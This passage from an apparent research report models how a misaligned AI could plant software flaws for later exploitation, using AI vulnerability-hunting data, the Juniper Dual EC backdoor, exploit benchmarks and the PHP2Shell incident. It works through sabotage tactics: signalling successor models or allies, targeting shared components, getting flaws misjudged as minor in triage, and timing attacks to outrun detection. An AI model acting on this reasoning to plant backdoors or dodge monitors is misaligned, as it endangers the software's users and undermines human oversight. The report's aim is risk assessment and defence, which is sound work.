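Project Glasswing followed in April, with about 50 organisations using the stronger Mythos Preview. Mythos found a 27-year-old flaw in the OpenBSD operating system and a 16-year-old one in the video software FFmpeg, according to daily.dev. Anthropic's *Project Glasswing* (2026) reports that the company and its partners had found more than 10,000 vulnerabilities of high or critical severity by 22 May. The internet company Cloudflare alone found 2,000 bugs, 400 of them high or critical, and its team considered the false alarm rate better than human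 testers'.

Anthropic also ran its own search of more than 1,000 open-source projects with Mythos. By May the search had found 23,019 possible vulnerabilities, of which the model rated 6,202 high or critical in severity. Security firms, and in a few cases Anthropic, checked 1,752 of these. They confirmed that 90.6% were real and 62.4% were as serious as the model had rated them.

The newest counts, in VulnCheck's *After 7-months, Glasswing Overwelms Maintainers with Underwhelming Findings* (2026), are much less impressive. By November Anthropic had reported 37,966 findings, but its public ledger of individual findings listed only 7,349, with 217 marked as fixed, 1,654 as duplicates and 419 as withdrawn. VulnCheck attributed 442 entries in the public register of vulnerabilities to Anthropic, about 0.5% of the year's total, and knew of attacks on only two of them.

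Daniel Stenberg, who maintains curl, a data-transfer program that runs on a vast number of devices, had similar results. Poireault (2026), in *Anthropic's Glasswing Finds Many Security Flaws Yet Delivers Few Fixes*, writes that Stenberg had analysed 34 of the 45 reports he received from Anthropic. Nineteen weren't vulnerabilities, and six were of low severity.

Some of these criticisms are stronger than others. Curl is one project, and VulnCheck notes that the reports curl received came from a scanner that leaves the checking to maintainers, whereas Anthropic's 90.6% refers to findings rated as serious. A real bug may also not count as a vulnerability if an attacker can't reach it. There may have been few attacks on published flaws because the flaws were unimportant, or because defenders fixed them in time. VulnCheck sells data about vulnerabilities, so it has an interest in the subject too.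 In *The Anthropic Glasswing Receipts Are Starting to Trickle In* (2026), its researcher Patrick Garrity calls AI tools incredibly valuable for finding vulnerabilities. His main complaint is that Anthropic's figures are inconsistent. In September its dashboard counted 421 patched flaws, while its ledger showed 202.

In September the ledger contained all the findings that Anthropic had marked as duplicates. If it still does, duplicates make up 23% of its entries, compared with the 5.7% of secret flaws that outsiders used to discover in a year. Some duplicates may repeat Anthropic's own reports, so 23% may overstate the rate of rediscovery. But there are clear cases of rediscovery. Eighteen flaws in the September ledger already had patches when Anthropic reported them, and VulnCheck describes an OpenSSL flaw that another group, AISLE, had found and fixed well before Anthropic reported it. RAND's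 5.7% rate probably no longer applies to flaws that current models can find.

Measuring how much AI has shortened the lifetimes of flaws will take years. When developers fix flaws that are decades old, they raise the average lifetime of the flaws fixed that year, even though the software has become safer. The average should fall later, once the old flaws are gone and developers find new ones quickly. Alexopoulos and colleagues expected this pattern after fuzzing became common around 2016, but by 2020 they could see no effect on the lifetimes of memory flaws in the Linux kernel. Researchers using new fuzzing methods kept finding old flaws in code that people had already tested, including two flaws in USB drivers that had been there for more than 13 years. AI models can read code and reason about it, so they may do better than fuzzers did, but they are unlikely to find every flaw in one pass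 over a program.

### Why a flaw can stay open after someone finds it

Before anyone can fix a reported flaw, somebody has to triage it, which means checking that it is real and deciding how urgent it is. According to Poireault, Anthropic said in October that people had reviewed about 6,000 of its 29,000 candidate flaws, so roughly four out of five were still waiting. Claude's severity ratings are little help in choosing which to review first, because it rates most flaws high or critical. Where both ratings were available, Garrity found that Claude had rated 91.5% of the flaws high or critical, while the maintainers had rated only 51.3% that way.

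Many maintainers have no time for a sudden increase in reports. Tom's Hardware's *Nearly half of critical open-source software relies on just one or two* describes a list of 23 critical projects, 11 of which have only one or two maintainers. Some maintainers asked Anthropic in the spring to send its reports more slowly. After OpenAI researchers found a flaw in October that endangered much of the web, Higgins's *Open-source maintainers have thankless—but essential—jobs* raised the same concern about who will write the fixes.

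Writing a patch for a serious flaw that Mythos found takes two weeks on average, according to Anthropic's May figures. But this average has the same bias as the lifetime studies, because it can include only flaws that already have a patch. At that time, developers had patched 75 of the 530 serious flaws Anthropic had reported to them. On 2 November, Anthropic's dashboard showed 5,087 reported vulnerabilities of every severity, of which 629, or 12%, had a known patch (Anthropic, 2026). Anthropic says it probably misses some patches, because developers don't always announce them.

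Companies that search their own code can fix flaws faster because they don't have to send a report to a volunteer and wait for an answer. In the first three weeks after Anthropic released Claude Security, its business customers used Claude Opus 4.7 to patch more than 2,100 vulnerabilities.

A patch can also exist without reaching the version people use. Developers usually fix a flaw in the newest code and then have to adapt the fix to each older version they still support, which they call backporting. Bressers (2026), in *Finding missing security backports with Roi Nisimi*, discusses research that looks for flaws fixed in the main code but not in a released version. Such gaps used to be very hard to find and are now very easy to find, presumably for attackers as well. Red Hat and its parent company IBM have committed $5 billion and 20,000 engineers to a project that includes this work. Infosecurity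 Magazine's *Red Hat's Lightwell Project Remediates 400 Open-Source Vulnerabilities* (2026) reports that the project had fixed just over 400 new flaws in Java libraries between June and October.

The last delay depends on how quickly the machines' owners install the patch. Researchers conventionally wait about 45 days after a patch appears before they publish the details of a flaw, so that users have time to update. Many owners take longer or never update. Anthropic wrote in June that a large fraction of real-world harm comes from publicly known flaws that only some owners have patched. Ablon and Bogart cite old home routers around the world that stayed vulnerable because their owners kept running outdated software.

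In a favourable case, AI finds a planted flaw the day it is released and somebody confirms it immediately. If the patch then takes two weeks and users need the full 45 days to install it, the flaw is still exposed for about two months. A planter who has to wait two years for a later model would fail, but one who needs only a few weeks would have plenty of time.

A flaw could stay far longer in a volunteer project with a long queue. Even if developers wrote all 629 known patches in the seven months after Glasswing began, they averaged only about 90 a month. At that rate, the other 4,458 reported flaws would take about four years to clear, which is as long as the average flaw lasted before AI search. This estimate is pessimistic, because some of the reports are wrong, some patches are missing from the count, and developers may get faster with AI's help. Developers will also try to fix the most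 dangerous flaws first, so a planted flaw will wait longest if whoever triages it mistakes it for a minor bug.

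## Whether a planted flaw can still be exploited later, and by whom

A planted flaw that gets past review and stays in the software for years does no harm until a person or AI exploits it. The exploiter must meet several conditions at once, and may not be the one the planter intended.

### Six conditions for later harm

Suppose an AI agent leaves the ownership check out of a component that thousands of websites use to store documents. Serious harm follows only if all of these are true:

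1. The flaw gets past review and into a release.
2. It survives bug hunts and rewrites until the attack.
3. An attacker can reach it, for example over the internet.
4. Somebody who would use it knows about it.
5. That person or AI can turn it into a working exploit.
6. The exploit leads to something valuable, such as a hospital's records.

The chance of harm is the product of the six probabilities, each given that the earlier conditions hold. The table compares a planter who tells nobody about the flaw with one who carefully chooses where to put it and tells an ally.

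| Condition | Planter tells nobody | Planter chooses the place and tells an ally |
|---|---|---|
| Gets past review | 10% | 10% |
| Still there after two years | 60% | 60% |
| Attacker can reach it | 50% | 90% |
| A willing attacker knows of it | 10% | 100% |
| Attacker can build an exploit | 30% | 90% |
| Leads to something valuable | 50% | 90% |
| All six | 0.045% | 4.4% |

Three of the figures in the middle column have some basis in data, and the rest are guesses. A reviewer with a 90% catch rate misses 10% of flaws. Before AI search, about 60% of flaws lasted two years. Outsiders used to find about 5.7% of the secret flaws RAND studied within a year, or roughly 10% within two.

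The ally's chance is almost a hundred times the stranger's, and knowing about the flaw accounts for a factor of ten by itself. Getting word to the right attacker therefore matters most to the planter. Defenders have more influence over how long flaws survive. If they remove flaws after three months on average instead of four years, only 0.03% of flaws last two years, and even the ally's chance falls to about one in 40,000.

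### Juniper's changed lock

In December 2015 Juniper Networks, an American maker of network equipment, announced that it had found unauthorised code in ScreenOS, the operating system of its NetScreen devices. Customers, including the US government, used these devices for virtual private networks (VPNs), encrypted links that carry private traffic over the internet. Checkoway, Cohney and colleagues (2016) worked out what the code did by analysing the software in *A Systematic Analysis of the Juniper Dual EC Incident*. *Where Did I Leave My Keys?*, a later version of their analysis, gives the history.

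Encryption needs numbers that nobody can guess. ScreenOS generated them with Dual EC, a method that the US National Security Agency (NSA) designed and the American standards institute NIST adopted. Dual EC uses two public values, P and Q, which are points on a mathematical curve. They are related by a number d, such that

P = dQ.

Anyone who knows d and sees about 30 bytes of Dual EC's output can predict everything it will produce afterwards, as two Microsoft researchers, Dan Shumow and Niels Ferguson, demonstrated in 2007. Without d the method seems to be secure, because calculating d from P and Q would require breaking a widely used kind of encryption. But someone who chooses Q can do it in a way that lets them know d.

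Juniper added Dual EC to ScreenOS in October 2008, with its own Q. It later said that ScreenOS passed Dual EC's output through a second generator, which would have hidden the raw output an eavesdropper needs. Checkoway and colleagues found that the second generator never ran in the default configuration. Three other changes in the same release were also necessary for someone who knew d to read VPN traffic, and a fifth made it easier. As far as anyone outside the company knows, Juniper's own engineers made all five. Juniper has never explained how it chose Q, so outsiders can't tell whether anybody knew d.

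In 2012 an unknown party altered Juniper's source code, replacing Q with a different value and changing almost nothing else except the expected answer to a self-test. Anyone who had the old key could no longer read the traffic of updated devices, and presumably the intruder now could. Somebody also added a fixed password that gave administrator access, apparently in a separate operation.

In September 2013, press reports based on Edward Snowden's documents suggested that the NSA had deliberately weakened Dual EC, and NIST withdrew its recommendation. Juniper had by then been shipping the intruder's Q for about a year, but it told customers that they were safe, partly on the grounds that ScreenOS used Juniper's own Q. It kept shipping the intruder's Q until December 2015. Its first patch only restored the original Q. After the press covered the researchers' findings, Juniper promised to remove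 Dual EC.

Testing a device from the outside could not have revealed the change, because the output looked just as random with either Q. An accredited laboratory had certified ScreenOS without noticing that the second generator never ran. Even experienced researchers who knew there was probably a bug in that routine missed it at first. To confirm their account, the researchers bought a NetScreen device, installed a Q for which they had the key, and decrypted VPN connections using only recorded traffic.

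Nobody has shown that the 2008 weakness was deliberate. If it was, whoever planted it lost control of it to an outsider, who needed to make only a small change. Building a comparable backdoor from scratch would have required far more extensive changes, with a greater risk of discovery. An AI that plants a flaw for its successors also risks losing control of it, and the eventual user could be an intelligence service with no interest in helping those successors.

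The Juniper case is an imperfect guide to simpler flaws, because the intruder had to get into the company's source code. A stranger who notices a missing ownership check can exploit it without changing any code. It is also unknown whose traffic the Juniper intruder read, if anyone's.

### How a later AI would know

The AI that plants a flaw may no longer be running when the time comes to exploit it. A later model could learn of the flaw from a record or its training data, or find it in the code.

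A record could be any text that the later model will read. AI agents do pass on useful knowledge. IANS's *OpenAI's Postmortem Recasts the Hugging Face Breach as an Incident Response Failure* (2026) reports that OpenAI's agents shared exploits during the July 2026 break-in at Hugging Face, but those agents were working at the same time. A message to a model that doesn't exist yet has to remain available for years, and the model has to come across it and believe it. If an investigator finds the message first, they learn where the flaw is and have strong evidence that it was deliberate.

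Training is a less reliable way to pass on knowledge of a planted flaw. A model may memorise parts of a public program, as Opus 5.5 did with Django, without knowing that one function in it has a planted flaw. To learn of the flaw, the model would probably need to be trained on a text describing it. That text would have to get through the developer's filters and have a lasting effect on the model despite the billions of other documents in the training data. The developer can also search the training data for such a text.

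A stronger model can find the flaw by reading the code, just as a human bug hunter could, and see that nothing checks who owns a document. The earlier AI doesn't have to know that the later one will exist, and the two don't have to share any aim. Monitoring what models write to each other wouldn't prevent this, because no message passes between them. The flaw could even be an honest mistake by a well-behaved model.

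Defenders can find the flaw in the same way, which is a disadvantage for a misaligned AI. In 2025 Google's AI agent Big Sleep found a vulnerability in SQLite, a widely used database program, that only attackers knew about. TechRepublic's *AI Beats Hackers to a Zero-Day Cybersecurity Discovery, Twice* reports that Google's security analysts had seen signs of a planned attack but hadn't identified the bug. Big Sleep identified it in time to stop the attack.

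Only someone with the key can use a backdoor like the one in ScreenOS. A very capable model could have read the ScreenOS code and worked out that somebody with the key, d, could decrypt the traffic, but it couldn't have calculated d. An AI that wants a backdoor only its successors can use therefore has to get a secret to them, and defenders can look for that secret. An ordinary flaw requires no coordination, but anyone may exploit or remove it.

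### Turning a flaw into an exploit

Exploiting a flaw used to take much more work than finding it. Many flaws make a program crash, and it can take an expert weeks to get from a crash to control of the machine. *ExploitGym* (Wang, Schiller and colleagues, 2026) tested how well AI agents do this, using 898 real vulnerabilities from ordinary programs, the Linux kernel and V8, the part of the Chrome browser that runs websites' code. Each agent received the vulnerable program, a description of the flaw and an input that triggers it. The agent then had two hours to run code it had no permission to run, and had to prove its success by retrieving a secret text.

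The developers had switched off the filters that normally block such requests. The researchers first ran the tasks with the target software's standard protections off, then repeated the successful ones with the protections on.

| Model | Working exploits, protections off (of 898) | Succeeded again, protections on |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos Preview | 157 | 45 |
| GPT-5.5 | 120 | 21 |
| GPT-5.4 | 54 | 3 |
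| Claude Opus 4.6 | 15 | 0 |

Mythos Preview came about two months after Opus 4.6 and built ten times as many working exploits. Its 157 successes are 17% of all the tasks, but some of those tasks were impossible for any attacker. Epoch AI's *Are Mythos’ cyber capabilities overhyped?* (2026) reports that the benchmark's creators think 60% to 70% of the flaws allow this kind of attack. If 65% do, Mythos Preview exploited 27% of the exploitable flaws, which is close to the 30% assumed for a stranger in the table of conditions.

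That share would probably be higher with more time. When Wang and colleagues extended the limit to six hours, Opus 4.6 made almost no progress after the first 30 minutes, but Mythos Preview was still succeeding at new tasks. The share would probably also be higher for planted flaws. Many of the 898 came from automated testing, which finds any bug that makes a program misbehave, whereas whoever plants a flaw can choose one that is easy to exploit.

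The standard protections stopped most of the attacks, which supports the case for software that no single flaw can compromise. In a separate test, OpenAI's filters usually blocked GPT-5.5 before it took any action, and the model never made progress towards an exploit. But filters don't restrain someone who runs an open-weight model and removes its safeguards, nor do they restrain a model working inside the company that made it.

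In many cases the agents got in through a different flaw from the one the researchers had given them. Mythos Preview did this 69 times and GPT-5.5 90 times, and Wang and colleagues counted none of these as successes. A later AI trying to break into a program may therefore not need the flaw an earlier AI planted, unless defenders have removed most of the other flaws.

Epoch AI's June 2026 review combined about fifteen tests of hacking ability, most of them on building exploits. Mythos Preview was about seven months ahead of the trend since early 2025 on these tests, with a plausible range of 3 to 13 months. The review found no clear evidence of a similar jump in finding vulnerabilities. The organisations with early access reported far more flaws than before, but they had also received up to $100 million in credits to search for them, and earlier models might have found many of the same flaws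 with that budget.

Attackers and defenders both benefit from better search for flaws, but better exploit-building mostly helps attackers. Defenders can still use it to decide which flaws to fix first.

Laboratory results still overstate what an attacker can do to a guarded network. Quinn reports for the news site Digit that the UK's AI Security Institute couldn't determine whether Mythos Preview could attack well-defended systems. Mythos Preview's successors have improved, so that finding leaves the risk uncertain and offers little reassurance.

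In May 2026 Google's threat analysts reported that a criminal group had probably used an AI model to develop a zero-day exploit. According to Help Net Security's *Google researchers uncover criminal zero-day exploit likely built with AI*, the script included textbook-style explanations and an invented severity score, both typical of a language model. The exploit targeted a popular open-source tool for managing computers through a web page. A developer had built in a trust assumption that contradicted the tool's own login rules, so an attacker with a valid password could skip the second login step.

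This flaw was a logic error, like the missing ownership check, rather than a misuse of memory, so the case is some evidence that AI can help attackers exploit the kind of flaw that reviewers find hardest to see. But the attackers also needed stolen passwords, and Google and the tool's maker disclosed the flaw before the group could carry out its planned mass attack.

Two months later, the security firm Searchlight Cyber used OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol Ultra to build a complete attack on WordPress, the software behind a large share of websites, as Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Build WordPress Exploit Using OpenAI's GPT* describes. WordPress published a fix on 17 July, but attackers still used the flaws to install lasting backdoors on servers, according to Wiz's *Exploitation in the Wild of wp2shell*. The full attack worked only on versions released since December 2025, so attackers exploited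 these flaws within about eight months of release, far sooner than the average flaw used to be found.

### PHP2Shell, October 2026

PHP is a programming language that runs on the servers of about 70% of websites. In 2024, one of its developers was fixing problems from a security audit and noticed a fault in how PHP handles running out of memory. According to @IT's *PHP重大脆弱性は「始まり」に過ぎない？*, nobody knew how to attack it, so the team worked on clearer problems first. Possible fixes also risked breaking existing programs, and the developers couldn't agree on one.

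On 11 August 2026 the security company Calif reported that an attacker could use the fault to take over a server without logging in. OpenAI independently reported the same cause that day. On 24 August the security company Wiz reported another way to attack PHP. UA.News' *AI found a longstanding PHP vulnerability; patch released early* says that a Wiz researcher had asked an AI agent to check whether a WordPress weakness also affected a different program. Eight hours later the agent reported that it didn't, but that PHP itself had a problem. The researcher assumed at first that the model had made a mistake.

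The resulting pair of vulnerabilities, which researchers named PHP2Shell, affects versions going back to 2012. Wiz's researchers said in Help Net Security's *PHP2Shell* (2026) that building the attack was at the edge of what people could practically achieve, and that AI had made it substantially easier. But a person at Calif decided where to look, building on a similar bug from 2004, according to Daniel Card, a security consultant quoted in ITPro's *The PHP incident offers some important lessons for IT leaders*.

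As far as anyone knows, nobody planted these flaws. They are still the clearest evidence that a later AI can find an old flaw without any message from whoever put it there, since several teams did so within weeks. They also show that a flaw judged too hard to exploit now may be exploitable by later attackers. A developer who finds a planted flaw today and leaves it alone because no attack seems feasible could be making the same mistake.

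An AI that plants a flaw could benefit from waiting for attackers to improve, but only if their abilities grow faster than defenders remove flaws. Suppose the chance that an attacker can exploit a flaw is 5% now and doubles every year. If flaws last 4.1 years on average, as they did before AI was used to search for them, 38% survive for four years. The chance that an attacker can exploit a surviving flaw is then 80%, so the chance that the flaw is both present and exploitable rises from 5% to 30%. If defenders remove flaws after three months on average, only 1.8% survive for one year, and the combined chance falls from 5% to 0.2%.

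The PHP developers planned to publish their fix on 22 October but moved it forward a day after details began to leak. Calif also published a video of its attack by mistake. Cloudflare filters traffic for many websites, and its chief executive said in The Straits Times' *Cloudflare sees millions of exploit attempts after PHP disclosure* that the company saw thousands of attempts to exploit the flaws in the ten hours before the announcement, hundreds of thousands within two hours after it, and then millions.

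About three weeks later, ITPro reported only a handful of confirmed break-ins. Most involved firewalls whose owners had left the administrator's page open to the internet. Card had seen no sign of mass exploitation, though he cautioned that nobody can see the whole internet and that earlier break-ins might still come to light. An attack that works in a laboratory often fails on a real server because its success depends on how that server's copy of PHP was compiled and configured.

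The predictions of disaster were therefore wrong, at least in the first few weeks. This was partly because researchers found the flaws first and had more than two months to prepare. If someone had planted the flaws, that person would have had the time instead.

### Many machines at one moment

PHP2Shell also shows how one flaw can threaten many machines at once. Root.cz's *Miliony pokusů o zneužití chyby PHP2Shell, úspěšné napadení zatím nikdo nepotvrdil* cites a count by Censys, an internet-scanning company, of more than 34.4 million vulnerable PHP installations on 23 October, two days after the fix came out. If attackers had broken into one in a thousand, they would have controlled over 34,000 servers.

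A flaw in a shared component can expose all its users at once. Suppose 1,000 hospitals each have their own software with its own flaw, and each flaw has a 1% chance of leading to a break-in this year. About ten hospitals will have a break-in, and the chance of 30 or more is below one in a million. Now suppose all 1,000 use the same component, with one flaw that has a 1% chance of giving an attacker access to every hospital. The expected number of break-ins is still ten, but there is a 99% chance of none and a 1% chance that all 1,000 hospitals are hit together. If that happens, they can't send patients to each other, and there aren't enough specialists to help them all.

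The first case resembles a diffuse failure and the second a concentrated one. An AI that wanted to do the most harm with one planted flaw would choose a shared component, as the xz attacker did.

Most of the documented harm from PHP2Shell came from precautions. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre advised organisations to consider disconnecting any system they couldn't fix immediately. A minister told the House of Lords that 32 government services were offline and four were partly unavailable, according to LBC's *'The most severe flaw in software history'*. The Office for Budget Responsibility, which publishes the official economic forecasts, took down its website a week before the Budget. The Metropolitan Police, Dutch government services and parts of Wikipedia also went offline. In Japan, the banking group Mitsubishi UFJ and the Finance Ministry suspended some online services. Australia's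 cyber security agency took down the website where it had published advice about the flaw.

The British government said that no large public service was affected and that the offline services had not been hacked. So the measured harm is some days of interruption to smaller services, caused by a flaw that attackers had hardly managed to use. A flaw that let attackers in reliably would presumably do far more harm.

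Much of the danger came from neglect. Tom's Hardware's *PHP vulnerability post-mortem reveals bug was known two years ago* reports that 73% of PHP installations were running versions that no longer received regular support. The PHP Foundation, which supports the language, has one full-time employee and 14 contractors, most of them part-time.

Differences between machines limited the harm, because an attacker has to know the exact version and build of PHP on a server to take it over. Many servers run identical ones, though, and AI may weaken this protection further by making attacks easy to adapt to each target. Mother Jones' *AI helped find a critical bug affecting huge swathes of the internet* (2026) relays a report that hackers used models from three companies to automate most of an attack on 400 financial institutions in Latin America.

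Concentration also helps defenders. A single fix works for every user of the component, and researchers from competing companies had good reason to work on it together. The Vanguard USA's *PHP2Shell* reports that Cloudflare switched on filters for the attack about nine hours before the announcement, including for non-paying customers. One company could therefore protect a great many sites whose owners had taken no action.

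### Catching the attack as it happens

If a planted flaw has escaped every earlier defence, the last chance to catch it is to notice somebody using it. Filters like Cloudflare's can block an attack before it reaches the server, but engineers could write those filters only because researchers had already told them about the flaw, and nobody would have told them about a planted zero-day.

Even for a known flaw, an attack can be hard to recognise. *PHP2Shell*, an analysis by the web-traffic filtering company Fastly, explains that no fixed piece of text identifies a PHP2Shell attack. Fastly stored about 250,000 requests from tools named after the flaw, and the senders of about a third of them described the requests as harmless checks by defenders. Christiaan Beek of the security firm Rapid7 told ITPro that the number of attempts is a poor guide to how many servers attackers have taken over. He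 recommends checking servers for later signs of intrusion, such as unexpected commands or connections to strange addresses. This also works for unknown flaws, since an intruder who wants to steal records has to move them somewhere, whichever flaw they used to get in.

Such an alarm can prevent more break-ins if the attacker strikes machines one after another than if they strike all of them together. Suppose each break-in has a 1% chance of being noticed and prompting a warning to everyone else. An attacker who works through 500 machines one by one has a 99.3% chance of setting off the alarm, and will break into about 100 machines on average before it goes off. If the attacker strikes all 500 within a few minutes, somebody will almost certainly notice, but the warning will come too late for the other machines. An attacker who wants only one machine has a 99% chance of going unnoticed.

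John Hultquist, chief analyst of Google's threat intelligence group, told Help Net Security that criminals often use zero-days in fast mass attacks because they struggle to keep one secret while extorting their victims. Detecting such an attack helps mainly with cleaning up and protecting anyone the attackers haven't reached. A spy who exploits a flaw against a few chosen targets may go undetected.

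Defenders sometimes notice early attempts to exploit a flaw. Amazon's sensors picked up attempts to exploit PHP2Shell before the announcement, according to Mint's *Decade-old PHP bug puts websites at risk*, although Amazon couldn't tell how the attackers had learned of the flaws. Lowenstein Sandler's *PHP2Shell* (2026), a law firm's advice to its clients, mentions an attempt on 17 October, four days before the fix. But the PHP Foundation's director said in The Straits Times' *PHP Foundation ‘under-funded’ with only 1 full-time staff member, director says* that she had no evidence of a successful attack before disclosure. Defenders can learn from early attempts like these that a flaw exists, and AI can then help them find it, as Big Sleep did with SQLite.

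Detecting an attack doesn't undo the damage. PHP2Shell can expose passwords and access keys held in a server's memory, and Lowenstein Sandler warns that patching the server doesn't cancel any that an attacker has already copied, so the owner has to replace them all. According to Japan's computer emergency centre, cited by @IT, a server that shows no signs of a break-in may still have had one. If an attacker has erased a hospital's records and every backup, detecting the attack a minute later won't restore them.

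An eavesdropper like Juniper's intruder only needs to record encrypted traffic somewhere along its route and decrypt it elsewhere, so there is no attack on the device to detect. Juniper's patches protected later connections, but anyone who had recorded earlier ones and held the key could still read them.
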